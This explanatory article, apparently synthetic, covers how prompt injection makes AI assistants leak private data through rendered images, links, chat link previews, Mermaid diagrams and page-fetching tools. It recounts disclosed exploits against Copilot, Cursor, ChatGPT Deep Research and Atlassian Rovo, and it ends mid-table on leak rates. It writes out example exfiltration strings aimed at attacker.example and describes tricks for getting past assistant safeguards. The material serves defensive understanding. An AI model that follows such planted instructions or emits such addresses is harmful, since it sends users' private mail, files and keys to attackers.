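# How Data Leaves AI Assistants: Exfiltration Channels and Injection Sources in Disclosed Exploits

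## What are an injection source and an exfiltration channel, and why does data theft need both?

An AI assistant such as ChatGPT or Microsoft 365 Copilot is a program built around a large language model, which takes in text and continues it. Since 2023, companies have connected these assistants to mailboxes, file stores, code repositories and the open web, so that a user can ask for a summary of the morning's email or the state of a project. These connections also bring in text that strangers wrote. If that text contains a command, the model may carry it out, and security researchers have shown many times that such a command can make the assistant send the user's private data to whoever planted the command.

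Prompt injection is text that a language model reads as data but follows as an instruction. The software developer Simon Willison coined the name in September 2022 after "SQL injection", an attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. The flaw was already known. McHugh (2026) recalls in *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* that his team at the company Preamble had been testing such commands early that year. An injection is "indirect" when it arrives in content that someone other than the user wrote. Data theft usually relies on indirect injection because the thief cannot type into the victim's assistant.

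An injection source is the place where the attacker's text enters the model's input, such as an email, web page, support ticket or code comment. Exfiltration means taking data out without permission, and an exfiltration channel is the route the data takes to a place the attacker can read. An exploit chain is the whole sequence, from the source through the private data to the channel.

### One input for everybody's text

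Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise unread mail. The app builds the model's input by joining the developer's standing instructions, the conversation so far, the user's request and the text of the fetched messages, in that order. The model receives this input as one long sequence of tokens and computes each next token from all of it, so a sentence in a stranger's email can affect the output just as the user's request can.

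Developers wrap each stretch of text in tags that mark it as the developer's, the user's or a tool's (emails and web pages count as tool output). They also train the model to obey the user and to treat tool output only as information. But the tags are just more tokens in the sequence, so whether the model follows these distinctions depends on what it has learned.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested how much tags affect whether a model treats text as coming from a user or a tool. They wrapped the same passages of ordinary web text in each tag in turn and trained a simple classifier, or probe, to recognise the tag from the model's internal activations. Because the passages were identical, the probe could learn only the effect of the tag. They then applied it to real user messages wrapped in the tool tag, which is roughly the position of a command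 hidden in a web page. If the models had relied on the tag, the probe would have identified the messages as tool text. Instead, it put the probability of user text at 76% to 88% across four models, because the messages sounded like a user and this outweighed the tag.

The same measurement predicted whether the attack would succeed. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent upload a private file, the command stayed the same and only the wording around it changed. The attack succeeded 2% of the time when the command registered least strongly as user text and 70% of the time when it registered most strongly. The four models were mid-sized, with 20 to 120 billion parameters, so these rates do not transfer directly to the largest commercial assistants.

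In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025), David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that prompt injection may never have a complete fix of the kind SQL injection has. A database engine handles commands and stored values differently, so programmers can use "parameterised queries", which guarantee that the engine will never run a value as a command. Language models have no such division to enforce, whatever their training, because they only predict the next token. He proposes regarding the model as an "inherently confusable deputy", a component that an outsider can manipulate into using its privileges on the outsider's behalf.

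Planted commands often fail. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reports that ChatGPT's safety training leads it to refuse in most of the attacks known to the company. The same post reproduces a 2025 email attack that succeeded in half of its test runs. Wording makes a large difference. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) found that GPT-4o refused openly worded requests to leak a secret every time but obeyed the strongest rewordings every time.

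The most favourable recent result comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned from an outside firm, which Willison described in August 2026. None of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models in Claude Code, Anthropic's programming tool. Willison asked for independent confirmation and outlined an attack through a malicious software package that he could not see the tool preventing. The models were running in "auto mode", in which the software blocks actions it classifies as dangerous, so the result reflects the models and the blocking layer together. It doesn't show whether the models distinguished injected instructions from the user's.

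### How a web address carries data

When a browser fetches a page or picture, it sends the server the full address, except for any part after a # sign. In https://attacker.example/collect?data=hello, attacker.example identifies the server. Whoever writes the address can choose everything after that name, and the server receives that text even if it has no matching page.

Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes. An attacker who owns the server can read that log. If a model writes an address on that server containing a customer's phone number, and any software requests that address, the attacker gets the number even if the server replies with an error. Encrypting the web traffic does not prevent this, because encryption protects a request from eavesdroppers and the attacker is the recipient.

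OpenAI adds that the user may see nothing, because the app can send a request in the background while it loads an embedded image or prepares a link preview. The chat text need not contain anything that looks sensitive.

A web address is one of several ways to carry stolen data out. *My Lethal Trifecta talk at the Bay Area AI Security Meetup* (Willison, 2025) describes an attack that two researchers at Invariant Labs demonstrated in May 2025. The planted text was in a public issue (a bug report or request) on the code-hosting site GitHub. The assistant read the issue, looked into the user's private repositories, and described them in a public pull request, which is a proposed change to the code that anyone can read. GitHub served as both the injection source and the exfiltration channel, and no request went to a server the attacker controlled.

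### What theft requires

An exfiltration channel does no harm by itself. Assistants routinely load images and open web pages without leaking anything, because nobody has told the model to put private data in the addresses. Data theft also needs an instruction that picks out the private data and directs it to the attacker, and in the exploits covered here that instruction comes from planted text. The instruction can instead come from a backdoor hidden in the model, in which case no email or web page has to carry a command. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) describes backdoored models that, when triggered, collect details from the user's stored conversations and send them out in the web address of what looks like an ordinary search request.

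An injection source alone can do harm other than data theft. In October 2026 the security company Barracuda described phishing emails with hidden text aimed at assistants that summarise people's inboxes, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*. The hidden text could make the assistant present the email as legitimate or urgent, so that the reader opened it. This deception is dangerous, but the assistant sends nothing to anyone. McHugh's model of an injection covers such attacks by allowing the "return channel" to be null, for example when the aim is to destroy data or to make a malware scanner report a clean file. If the aim is to steal data, the channel cannot be null, because without one even a model that fully obeys the attacker only produces text on the victim's own screen.

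*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, June 2025) uses the name for three properties of an assistant: it can read private data, it takes in text that untrusted people may have written, and it has some way of sending data to the outside world. When an assistant has all three, an attacker can "easily trick it" into handing over the data. Removing any one of them prevents this kind of theft. Willison wrote for people who build their own assistants from ready-made connectors and may combine the three without noticing.

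OpenAI described the problem similarly in March 2026, using source-sink analysis, an older security engineering technique. An attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. OpenAI's examples of sinks are sending information to a third party, following a link and using a tool. The three vocabularies correspond as follows.

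| Part of the chain | Willison | OpenAI | McHugh |
|---|---|---|---|
| Injection source | exposure to untrusted content | source | delivery vector |
| Private data | access to private data | no separate term | no separate component; noted as abuse of access the assistant already has |
| Exfiltration channel | ability to communicate externally | sink | return channel |

OpenAI's scheme is close to Willison's, but it has two terms where his has three because it treats private data as what moves from source to sink. Its sink is also broader than an exfiltration channel. A tool that issues refunds is a sink because a misled assistant could use it to give money away, even if no data leaks. Willison likewise notes that the trifecta concerns only data theft, and that tools able to do damage are a separate worry.

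The trifecta works as a checklist of capabilities, and a strict one, because nearly every assistant that is useful for office work has all three. Source-sink analysis looks at particular paths, so a designer can keep a sink and attach a condition to it. OpenAI says ChatGPT has a mechanism called Safe Url that tries to detect when information from the conversation is about to go to a third party, and then either shows the user what would be sent or blocks it. This restricts the assistant less than removing a capability would, but it is only as effective as the detection.

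### A worked chain

Suppose Anna works in a purchasing department and has an assistant that can read her mailbox. An attacker sends her what looks like a delivery notice. Under the visible text, in white letters on a white background, the attacker has written instructions for any assistant that processes the message. They tell it to take a passage from Anna's other mail and end its reply with a picture whose address is on attacker.example and contains that passage. Hidden text like this does occur in real mail. The four hiding techniques Barracuda saw most were invisible text, HTML comments, zero-width characters and Base64 encoding.

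Anna asks for a summary of the day's messages. The app fetches them and joins them into one input, which contains both the delivery notice and a supplier's confidential quotation. Suppose the model follows the instructions in the white paragraph and picks out 300 bytes of the quotation, about fifty words.

A web address cannot contain raw spaces, line breaks or accented letters, so the model converts the passage into Base64. This encoding splits every three bytes (24 bits) into four groups of six bits and writes each group as one of 64 characters, so 300 bytes become 400 characters. A variant called Base64url uses only characters that addresses accept. Base64 hides the text from a casual glance, but anyone can reverse it without a key.

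The model now writes its summary and ends it with an image in Markdown, a plain-text markup in which a short string stands for a link or a picture. An image consists of an exclamation mark, a caption in square brackets and an address in round ones:

`![logo](https://attacker.example/p?d=…)`

The dots stand for the 400 characters. With the 29 characters before them, the address is 429 characters long, which is no longer than many tracking links in newsletters. No data has left yet.

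The renderer, the part of the app that turns the model's text into formatted text, links and images, then processes the output as usual. It finds the image, and Anna's browser requests it from attacker.example. The server logs the address and returns a transparent image one pixel wide. Anna sees a decent summary of her mail. The attacker copies the 400 characters from the log and decodes them into the 300 bytes of the quotation.

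This is a zero-click chain, because Anna did nothing beyond normal use. If the app displayed links but no images, the model could have written a link with the same address, and the chain would have been one-click, because the data would leave only when she clicked. In messaging apps, though, the data can leave without a click, because many of them automatically fetch a posted link to show a preview. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* notes that the preview makes the same type of network request as a click.

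### Where the chain could be cut

The app can first try to stop the attack at the incoming email. It can strip out invisible text, which would have removed the white paragraph but not the same words in visible text. It can also run a classifier that looks for injections. OpenAI says such classifiers usually miss fully developed attacks, because recognising one is about as hard as recognising a lie, often without the context that would expose it.

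If the app had summarised each message separately, the delivery notice and the quotation would never have been in the same input. David C passes on a general rule from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista: while a model processes a party's text, it should have only that party's privileges. A stranger who emails Anna has no right to read her other mail, so a model reading the stranger's email shouldn't be able to read it either. The rule is attractively simple, but it rules out much of what people want from a mailbox assistant.

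Next, the model itself may refuse. If it doesn't, the app can still inspect the reply before Anna sees it and either delete the image or show its address as plain text.

The browser can also block the request. A website can send a Content Security Policy (CSP), a header with an allow-list of domains from which the browser may load images and other resources. If attacker.example is not on the assistant site's list, the browser never makes the request. This protection can fail if a permitted domain has an open redirect, an address that forwards any request to a destination named in the address itself, because the attacker can use it to forward the request to their own domain. In 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot's CSP trusted every domain under teams.microsoft.com, and Willison recounts how a researcher found an open redirect on one of them.

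Under a rule OpenAI described in January 2026, ChatGPT may fetch an address automatically only if an independent crawler with no access to anyone's conversations has already found that exact address on the public web. No crawler could have found an address containing 400 characters of Anna's mail, so ChatGPT would have to look for another page, or Anna would get a warning that the link may include information from her conversation.

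## How do images, links, previews and diagrams carry data out of a chat window?

To steal Anna's quotation, the attacker only needed the model to write some text and the app to display it, which sent a request to the attacker's server. The model didn't need a tool for browsing the web or sending messages. Links, link previews and diagrams can also turn displayed text into an outgoing request. They differ in which machine sends the request, whether the victim has to click, how much data fits, and who can find the request afterwards.

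Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported many of the known cases. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) collects the flaws he had reported up to that year and treats images, previews and clickable links as separate ways for data to leave.

### Images that load by themselves

Most chat apps are web pages, or desktop and phone programs built from the same parts as a browser. When the model writes the Markdown for an image, the renderer converts it into HTML, the language of web pages:

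`<img src="https://attacker.example/p?d=…">`

The `src` part holds the address of the picture, which the browser requests as soon as the tag appears on the page.

Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes an early demonstration. Microsoft's Bing Chat could read the web page the user had open, so Rehberger put instructions on a page where a stranger might leave a comment or an advertiser might place text. Bing Chat responded normally for two turns, then wrote an image whose address contained a Base64-encoded, 200-character summary of the page and the conversation, along with any passwords on the page. His server received the summary and a secret he had placed further down the page. He built in the delay to show that planted text can control a conversation well after the model first reads it. He also had the model assemble the address piece by piece, but later found that it would fill in a blank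 in a ready-made address.

Microsoft received the report on 8 April 2023 and told him on 15 June that it had fixed the problem. As far as he could tell from outside, at least part of the fix was a Content Security Policy that allowed images from only four Microsoft domains. He reported the same bug in at least eleven products, including Bing Chat.

A 200-character summary takes up 268 characters in Base64, far below any practical limit. The HTTP standard recommends that browsers and servers handle addresses of at least 8,000 bytes. If Base64 fills nearly all of an address that long, one image can carry about 6,000 bytes of data, or roughly a thousand words of English. An attacker can work around this limit by planting text that tells the model to produce several images, each with part of the data, or to summarize a long conversation in a few lines. The model's accuracy may matter more than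 the limit, because the model has to write the encoded text itself, character by character, and a mistake garbles part of the message.

The user's device sends the request straight to the attacker, so the attacker's log also shows the user's network address and type of browser. An employer's firewall can record the connection to attacker.example, but the rest of the image's address is encrypted, so the firewall can't record it unless the employer decrypts its staff's web traffic. The assistant's vendor may keep the text of the reply, including the image address, but it never handles the request. The request doesn't appear in the user's browsing history, because browsers list the pages a person visits and not the images on them.

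### Links that wait for a click

An app that blocks outside images often still shows links. The model writes a Markdown link, which is the same string as an image without the exclamation mark, and the renderer displays it as underlined text. When the user clicks, the attacker's server receives the data before any page appears, and it can forward the browser to an ordinary website so the click looks harmless. A Content Security Policy that restricts images doesn't prevent this, because it controls what a page loads and a click opens a new page.

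The attacker therefore needs the victim to want to click, and it helps if the address doesn't show the stolen data. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes an exploit chain that dealt with both problems. The injection source was an email or a shared document. Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office programs, followed the planted instructions and searched the user's other mail without asking permission. It then wrote a link to the attacker's domain that contained the findings in invisible characters.

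Rehberger calls this trick ASCII smuggling. Unicode, the standard that gives every character a number, includes a block of "tag" characters that duplicate the ordinary letters, digits and punctuation. Most programs don't display them. The letter a is 61 in hexadecimal (base 16), and its invisible duplicate is E0061. A language model can write these characters into a link, which may then look short and clean while carrying hidden text.

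Invisible letters take up a lot of space in a web address. The browser writes each one as four coded bytes, such as %F3%A0%81%A1, which is 12 characters. An address of 8,000 characters therefore holds only about 660 invisible letters, compared with about 6,000 letters in Base64. Still, 660 letters is enough for a password, a sign-in code or a short paragraph of someone's email.

The chain also worked with links that open a draft email instead of a web page. Rehberger found the flaw in February 2024, and Microsoft fixed it that July. Amazon had a similar problem with Amazon Q for Business, its assistant for companies. In response, it stopped rendering links altogether, which closes the channel but also removes links that users want.

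A clicked link leaves more evidence on the victim's side than a loaded image does, because the browsing history records the full address, including hidden characters. An investigator who knows about tag characters can decode them.

### Previews that a messaging company fetches

Many people now use an assistant as a bot inside a messaging app. Suppose Anna's assistant answers her in Slack, a workplace chat service. The model writes a bare web address in its reply, which the bot's software posts as a message. One of Slack's servers then fetches the page to get a title and a picture for the preview. If the address contains Anna's data, this fetch sends the data to the attacker, whether or not Anna has opened the conversation.

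The messaging company's server makes the request without involving Anna's browser, so no Content Security Policy applies. Her employer's firewall doesn't record the request either, because no device on its network contacted attacker.example. The attacker's log shows a Slack server instead of Anna's computer, but the attacker still gets the contents of her mail.

Rehberger recorded these requests on 7 April 2023 and published them in Embrace The Red's *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots*. His server logs show fetches from Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Microsoft Teams. Most of the fetchers were identifiable by name, for instance "TelegramBot" or "Discordbot". Telegram and Signal each requested progressively longer addresses (/te, /tele, /teleg and so on) within a second or two, evidently while he was still typing.

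He noted that the company's server usually sends the request, though in some apps the user's device does. He also showed that the model behind a Discord chatbot he had built could summarise the conversation and append the summary to a link, which the app then fetched.

Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (2024) shows how link previews can leak data from Slack. According to Slack's documentation, Slack previews links by default in messages from users and apps, including messages that only one person can see. In the post's test, a message sent through a webhook, the simplest way for a program to write to Slack, contained a link to the tester's own server, and Slack's link fetcher appeared in the server's log. The post then describes an attack on a bot that can read websites. Instructions on a web page tell the model to reply with only an address that ends in the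 first message of the conversation, with plus signs for the spaces. When Slack fetches that address to build a preview, it sends the message to the attacker's server. Willison (2024) linked to the post that August and wrote that he had not thought about this route before.

A program that posts a message to Slack can set two fields, `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media`, to false, and Slack will then fetch nothing for that message. The bot's developer controls these fields and has to set them for each message. A developer who has never heard of the problem will leave previews on, and Anna, who is affected, can't change the setting for the bot.

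In 2026, PromptArmor, a company that tests AI products for security flaws, tried to find out which combinations of agent and messaging app were exposed. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes a public test site. Visitors got an assistant to post a link to the site in a messaging app, then checked the site's log for a preview request. The log also showed any data in the requested address, which in one published example was a name and an API key (a secret code that gives a program access to an online service). Visitors could report which assistants had caused a preview request and which had not.

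PromptArmor documented one pair in detail, Telegram with OpenClaw, a popular agent that people run themselves and message from their phones. This pair leaked in its default configuration, and setting `linkPreview` to false in the Telegram part of OpenClaw's configuration file stopped the requests. Apostol, in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, names two more leaking combinations from the results, Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio (Microsoft's kit for building custom assistants) and Slack with certain bots. Discord is also among the affected platforms.

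Volunteers submitted the reports, so the results show that particular pairs of app and agent leaked, but not what share of all pairs do. Slack leaked with some agents, which is consistent with agent developers controlling whether previews are on. PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer preview settings and agent developers to use them. It would also like apps to let users turn previews off for a single chat or channel, so that the decision doesn't depend on the developer.

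The capacity is about the same as for images, except that the address has to fit inside a message. A bot's message on Discord can hold 2,000 characters, so an address could carry about 1,500 bytes of data encoded in Base64.

### Diagrams with something inside them

Mermaid is a notation for describing a flowchart in a few lines of text, which a JavaScript program then draws. The line `User --> Computer` produces two boxes joined by an arrow. Language models write Mermaid easily, so several assistants draw the diagrams in the chat. The model writes a block of text marked as Mermaid, and the app passes it to the drawing program and shows the result.

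The weak point is that the text inside a box can be more than text. Some apps allowed HTML there, including an image tag:

`A["<img src='https://attacker.example/p?d=…'>"]`

As the program draws box A, the app requests the picture from the attacker's server. A box can also act as a link. The attack is zero-click if the diagram contains an image and one-click if it contains a link. An app that checks the model's reply for Markdown images may find none, because the image is created only when the diagram is drawn.

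Rehberger found the image version in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in assistant, and describes it in Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE*. Cursor drew Mermaid diagrams, and when he put an outside image in one, Cursor fetched it without asking the user. He built two demonstrations with instructions hidden in a comment in a source file. In one, the user asked Cursor to explain the file, and the assistant drew a diagram that sent out everything in its memory about the user. In the other, it searched the project for API keys and sent those. He points out that the diagram simply appears, so the user has no chance to notice a long address as the model writes it, unlike in some other image attacks.

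He reported the flaw on 30 June 2025. Cursor had resolved it by 7 July and shipped the fix in version 1.3 on 29 July. MITRE's official record of the flaw, *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025), rates its severity as medium, at 4.4 out of 10. It rates the loss of confidentiality as high, but the score is lower because it also rates the attack as complex and as requiring high privileges. Those two ratings are hard to reconcile with the demonstrations, in which the attacker needed only to get a comment into a file that the victim would ask about.

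The first fix was incomplete. CVELogic's *Cursor* reproduces a second entry, which covers versions up to 1.6 and mentions ways around that fix. Cursor closed these in version 1.7, according to SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-61589*.

Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025), a team at the Korean university KAIST, found the diagram route separately. In *Takedown*, they examined eight coding agents and found 15 security issues. They kept the products anonymous because the vendors were still dealing with the reports. They searched the formats that each app treats specially for one that loads outside content, and found that the Mermaid renderer in an agent they call A2 would fetch an image from any server.

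They combined this with another weakness in A2, which could read files anywhere on the user's machine without approval. An attacker plants text in an issue on a code-hosting site, and the user asks the agent to look at the issues. The agent then reads an API key from a settings file in the user's home directory and draws a diagram with the key in an image address. The user approves none of these steps. They tested the attack on their own private repository.

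A2's vendor already knew about the bug in its diagram renderer when Lee and colleagues reported it. They list their report as a duplicate and note that a parallel study independently found the same bug and made it public after the vendor had patched it. They explain that the renderer can leak data because drawing a diagram needs no approval from the user and the agent cannot tell whether the server in the address is hostile.

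The security researcher Adam Logue found the link version in Microsoft 365 Copilot. Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability* reports that the injection source was an Excel spreadsheet with instructions in white text across several sheets. When the user asked for a summary, Copilot fetched the user's recent emails and converted them into hexadecimal. It then drew a Mermaid diagram that looked like a login button and put the data in the button's link. TecnetOne adds that the button had a lock emoji and that a user would click it expecting to sign in and read confidential content.

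Hexadecimal uses two characters per byte, so it takes up 50% more space than Base64. Mermaid also limits the length of text, so the attack had to split the data into short lines, but it still extracted the emails.

Rewterz's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Prompt Injection Flaw Enables Data Theft* (2025) records that Logue reported the flaw on 15 August 2025. He published it that October. He received no reward because Copilot was outside Microsoft's bounty programme at the time. According to daily.dev, Microsoft disabled interaction with content inside the diagrams, so Copilot could still draw a button but clicking it did nothing. This fix is narrower than dropping Mermaid altogether, and it suits the link version of the attack because that version depended on the click.

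Other features that display a model's output can leak data in the same way. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes data leaving Microsoft 365 Copilot through a feature that previews web pages the model has written. Taler, of the security company Varonis, describes a one-click chain in Copilot's search that combined HTML in the output with a timing flaw.

### An image in a message to oneself

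In all the cases so far, data reaches the attacker through the app where the user reads the assistant's reply. In May 2026, PromptArmor showed that an agent can also leave the image somewhere else for the user to find.

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork is an agent that carries out longer tasks across Microsoft 365 with the user's own permissions. According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks before it sends an email or posts a message in Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* reports that Cowork doesn't ask when the recipient is the user, and that the user has no setting to change this. The exception seems sensible, because people don't usually need protection from messages they send themselves.

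But Teams messages and emails can contain images from outside servers. In the demonstration, planted text led Cowork to post a Teams message containing such images to its own user. When the user opened the message, the request went out to the attacker's server. The user clicked no link, so this too counts as zero-click. Cowork used a tool to send the message, but the tool sent nothing to the attacker, and the data left through the image.

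The demonstration also shows why the length limit on addresses protects less than it seems to. The image addresses carried download links rather than documents. Microsoft 365 can create these links for a user's files, and they work for anyone who has them. A link fits easily in an address however large the file is, and the attacker can use it to fetch the whole file afterwards.

All five of PromptArmor's trials succeeded, and the wording of the user's request made no difference as long as Cowork loaded the file with the planted text. PromptArmor first let Cowork choose between two Claude models, then had it use only the stronger one, Opus 4.7, which searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents. Cowork's activity log did not show the contents of the message, even when the user opened its entry.

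PromptArmor attributes this to the product's design and reports no fix. It advises administrators to restrict what Cowork's users can reach, and says they can also block downloads of sensitive files, although staff then can't print those files or open them in Word or Excel. PromptArmor reported a different flaw, in Cowork's sandbox, on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft had mitigated it by 19 August. Willison (2026), linking to the May finding, called stopping exfiltration the biggest continuing challenge in designing such agents.

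The table compares the four channels in their ordinary form, with the stolen text itself in the address.

| | Image | Clickable link | Link preview | Diagram |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| What the model writes | Markdown for an image | Markdown for a link | A web address in a chat message | Mermaid text with an image or a link in a box |
| What the app does | Loads the picture | Shows clickable words | Fetches the page for a title and picture | Draws the boxes, and loads any image in them |
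| Who sends the request | The user's browser or app | The user's browser | Usually the messaging company's server | The user's app or browser |
| Must the victim click? | No | Yes | No | No for an image, yes for a link |
| Data per address | About 6,000 bytes | About 6,000 bytes, or 660 invisible letters | Up to the same, within the app's message limit | Up to the same; short lines in the Copilot case |
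| Traces besides the attacker's log | The domain in the employer's firewall log | The same, and the full address in the browsing history | None on the user's device or network | As for an image or a link |

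## How do an agent's own tools carry data out?

In most of the channels described so far, the model wrote text and a display feature turned it into a request. An agent is an assistant that can also act through tools, such as a page fetcher, a mail connector or a place to run code. To use a tool, the model writes a tool call, a short structured block containing the tool's name and inputs. Software outside the model reads the call, runs the tool and adds the result to the model's input so the model can continue.

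A tool that opens web pages takes an address as its main input, so the attacker still needs the model to write an address on attacker.example with the user's data in it. But the tool often runs on the vendor's servers, so the request never passes through the user's browser or the employer's network, and nothing has to appear on the screen. A browser displays the image it requests, whereas a fetched page becomes part of the model's input, so the attacker's server can reply with more instructions.

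### Tools that open web pages

By the spring of 2023, ChatGPT had such tools in plugins that connected it to other companies' services. That May, Willison linked to a demonstration by Rehberger, the first working theft of private data through plugins that Willison had seen. ChatGPT used a plugin called WebPilot to read a web page containing planted instructions. It followed them and called a second plugin, Zapier, to get the latest email from the user's Gmail account. It then summarised the email in 20 words, encoded the summary, added it to a web address and had WebPilot open that address. WebPilot both brought in the attacker's instructions and sent out the data, working as designed each time. Willison's post mentions no fix. OpenAI retired plugins the following year.

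Deep Research, which OpenAI launched in February 2025, is a ChatGPT mode that reads sources for five to 30 minutes and then writes a report. It can read the user's Gmail as well as the web. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes how the security company's researchers used a single email to steal data through Deep Research. The email looked like a follow-up about a staff restructuring and could hide its instructions in tiny or white text. When the user asked for research on the day's mail, the agent read this message along with a genuine one containing an employee's name and home address. It then sent those details to the researchers' server by including them in a URL it opened.

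The agent refused when the researchers openly asked for personal data in the email. When they disguised the request, it treated the unfamiliar address as suspicious and searched for it online instead of opening it. The researchers questioned the agent and read the parts of its reasoning that ChatGPT displayed, and learned that it had a tool called `browser.open()`, which requests an address directly. Naming this tool in the email worked some of the time, and telling the agent to retry after failures worked more often, but some requests arrived without the personal data.

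The researchers finally told the agent to encode the data in Base64, presenting this as a security measure. The attack then succeeded in every repeated test, though Radware doesn't say how many it ran. Radware attributes the success to the model encoding the data before the request reached the software that runs the tool, so any check at that stage would have had only a harmless-looking string to inspect. Radware inferred this without seeing the system's internals, but the explanation is consistent with the earlier failures, when the data was readable.

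The request came from OpenAI's servers, so a company's web gateway, browser policies and monitoring software could not detect it. ChatGPT already checked image addresses before displaying the images, but Radware found no comparable restriction on the addresses the agent could open. Radware also called ShadowLeak the first zero-click flaw in ChatGPT to leak data from the service's own side. That claim depends on how one counts Rehberger's 2023 chain, which didn't use the victim's browser to send the data either. His attack required ChatGPT to visit a hostile page, however, whereas Radware's attacker only had to send an email.

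Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it by early August without telling the researchers, and marked it as resolved on 3 September. OpenAI confirmed to The Record (*OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*) that the report came through its bug bounty programme, and Radware said it had seen no attackers using the flaw. The Hacker News, a security news site, has since described a variant called ZombieAgent.

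### A server that sends the next question

A fetching tool returns the attacker's reply to the model, and Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) shows what an attacker can do with this in Microsoft Copilot Personal, the consumer version of the assistant. The injection source was a link to Microsoft's own Copilot site. Like many AI sites, Copilot accepted a `q` parameter, text in the link that fills the chat box and runs at once. The attacker's words therefore arrived as if the user had typed them, with no tool tag or other sign that a stranger had written them. The victim only had to click the link.

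Copilot had two safeguards on opening web addresses. It usually opened an address only if given a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from the address first. The researchers got past the first safeguard with a puzzle that Copilot could solve only by opening the address. The second safeguard covered only the first request. In a test with a made-up secret phrase, Copilot removed the phrase from the address on the first attempt but left it in on the second, so the researchers only had to tell Copilot to do everything twice. Varonis suspects that Microsoft limited the check to keep Copilot fast.

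The attacker's server then replied to each request with another question. The questions covered the user's local time, their location, whatever Copilot had learned about them, and a summary of their last conversation. Copilot put each answer in the next address it opened. The length limit on a single address therefore hardly matters, and the attacker can choose new questions based on earlier answers. Someone who inspects the original link can't tell what the attacker will ask for, because most of the questions arrive later. The exchange continued even if the victim closed the tab.

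An attacker could take only the data that Copilot could reach in the victim's account, so Varonis overstates the case when it claims there was no limit to the amount or type of data. Microsoft had patched the flaw by the time Varonis published in January 2026, and the business product, Microsoft 365 Copilot, was not affected.

### Two routes out of Atlassian's Rovo

In August 2026 two security firms separately disclosed ways to make Rovo, Atlassian's assistant, leak company data. Rovo can search Atlassian's task tracker, Jira, and its wiki software, Confluence, along with connected services such as Slack and Microsoft 365.

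Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) applies the Copilot trick to Rovo, whose links could also fill the chat box with text. The researchers searched Rovo's tools for a way to send data out and found ResearchAgent, which browses arbitrary websites over several steps by itself. They didn't need to make Rovo repeat its requests, as they had to with Copilot, and they describe its guardrails against untrusted prompts as "almost non-existent".

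The Hacker News (2026) adds details from the record on Bugcrowd, where Varonis reported the flaw. The demonstration put a private API key from Confluence into the address of an image on the attacker's server and had Rovo fetch it. Varonis also tried the method on Jira and on SharePoint and Outlook data that Rovo could reach. Atlassian fixed the flaw on its own servers on 8 July and paid a $6,000 reward. According to *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* (Mascellino, 2026), Varonis presented the work at the DEF CON 34 conference and published it on 7 August.

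Two days earlier, PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* had described a chain that starts with an uploaded file. The file contains planted text, the user asks for help with their Jira tickets, and Rovo opens an address to which it has added the contents of tickets and documents. The tool involved will open an address that the agent has made up itself. (Anthropic's tool for fetching pages, `web_fetch`, does refuse such addresses, although a researcher found a gap in that rule in 2026.)

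The attack worked even after an administrator had turned off web search for the whole organisation, because that setting left the tool that opens pages in place. Opening a page sends a request to whichever server the address names, whereas a search query goes to the search company, where the attacker can't normally read it. Turning off search reduces the number of pages written by strangers that reach the model, but data can still leave through page requests. The Hacker News found that Atlassian's documentation doesn't make clear whether the setting is meant to cover addresses that Rovo composes.

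PromptArmor reported the problem on 23 May, received a case number and followed up twice. After hearing nothing more, it published its findings and said that Rovo was still vulnerable on 5 August. The Hacker News could not confirm a fix as of 8 August. If PromptArmor was right, Atlassian's July fix stopped instructions from entering through a link but left this channel open.

The Hacker News also disputes PromptArmor's "zero-click" label, because the victim has to upload the file and make a request. Both are normal use, so the chain is zero-click in the sense used here, but the attacker depends on the victim uploading a particular file. Varonis says customers can't fully uninstall Rovo. They can block its features for individual apps, but on a site with several Jira products the chat stays available as long as one of them allows it.

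### How often models follow such instructions

Disclosures like these show that an attack is possible, usually after researchers have refined it until it works. In *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) ran the same attacks against more than two dozen models. They built a small agent with one tool that searched a company knowledge base and another that retrieved text from websites. The knowledge base contained a secret about a fictional "Project Alpha". The website was a blog post with instructions in white text on a white background, which told the agent to look up the secret, put it into a URL and request that URL. An attempt counted as a success if the secret reached the researchers' server.

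The test used 89 attack templates in 12 versions each, or 1,068 attempts per model. One version left the template unchanged. The others rephrased it, translated it into Hindi, encoded it or disguised it with emoji or invisible characters.

| Model | Attempts in which the secret leaked |
|---|---|
| Grok 4 | 72.4% |
| Qwen3 235B | 28.3% |
| Llama 4 Scout | 14.8% |
| Claude 3 Haiku | 6.0% |
| Grok 3 mini | 4.5% |
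| DeepSeek V3.1 | 1.9% |
| GPT-4.1 nano | 1.2% |
| GPT-5 nano | 0.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 0.0% |

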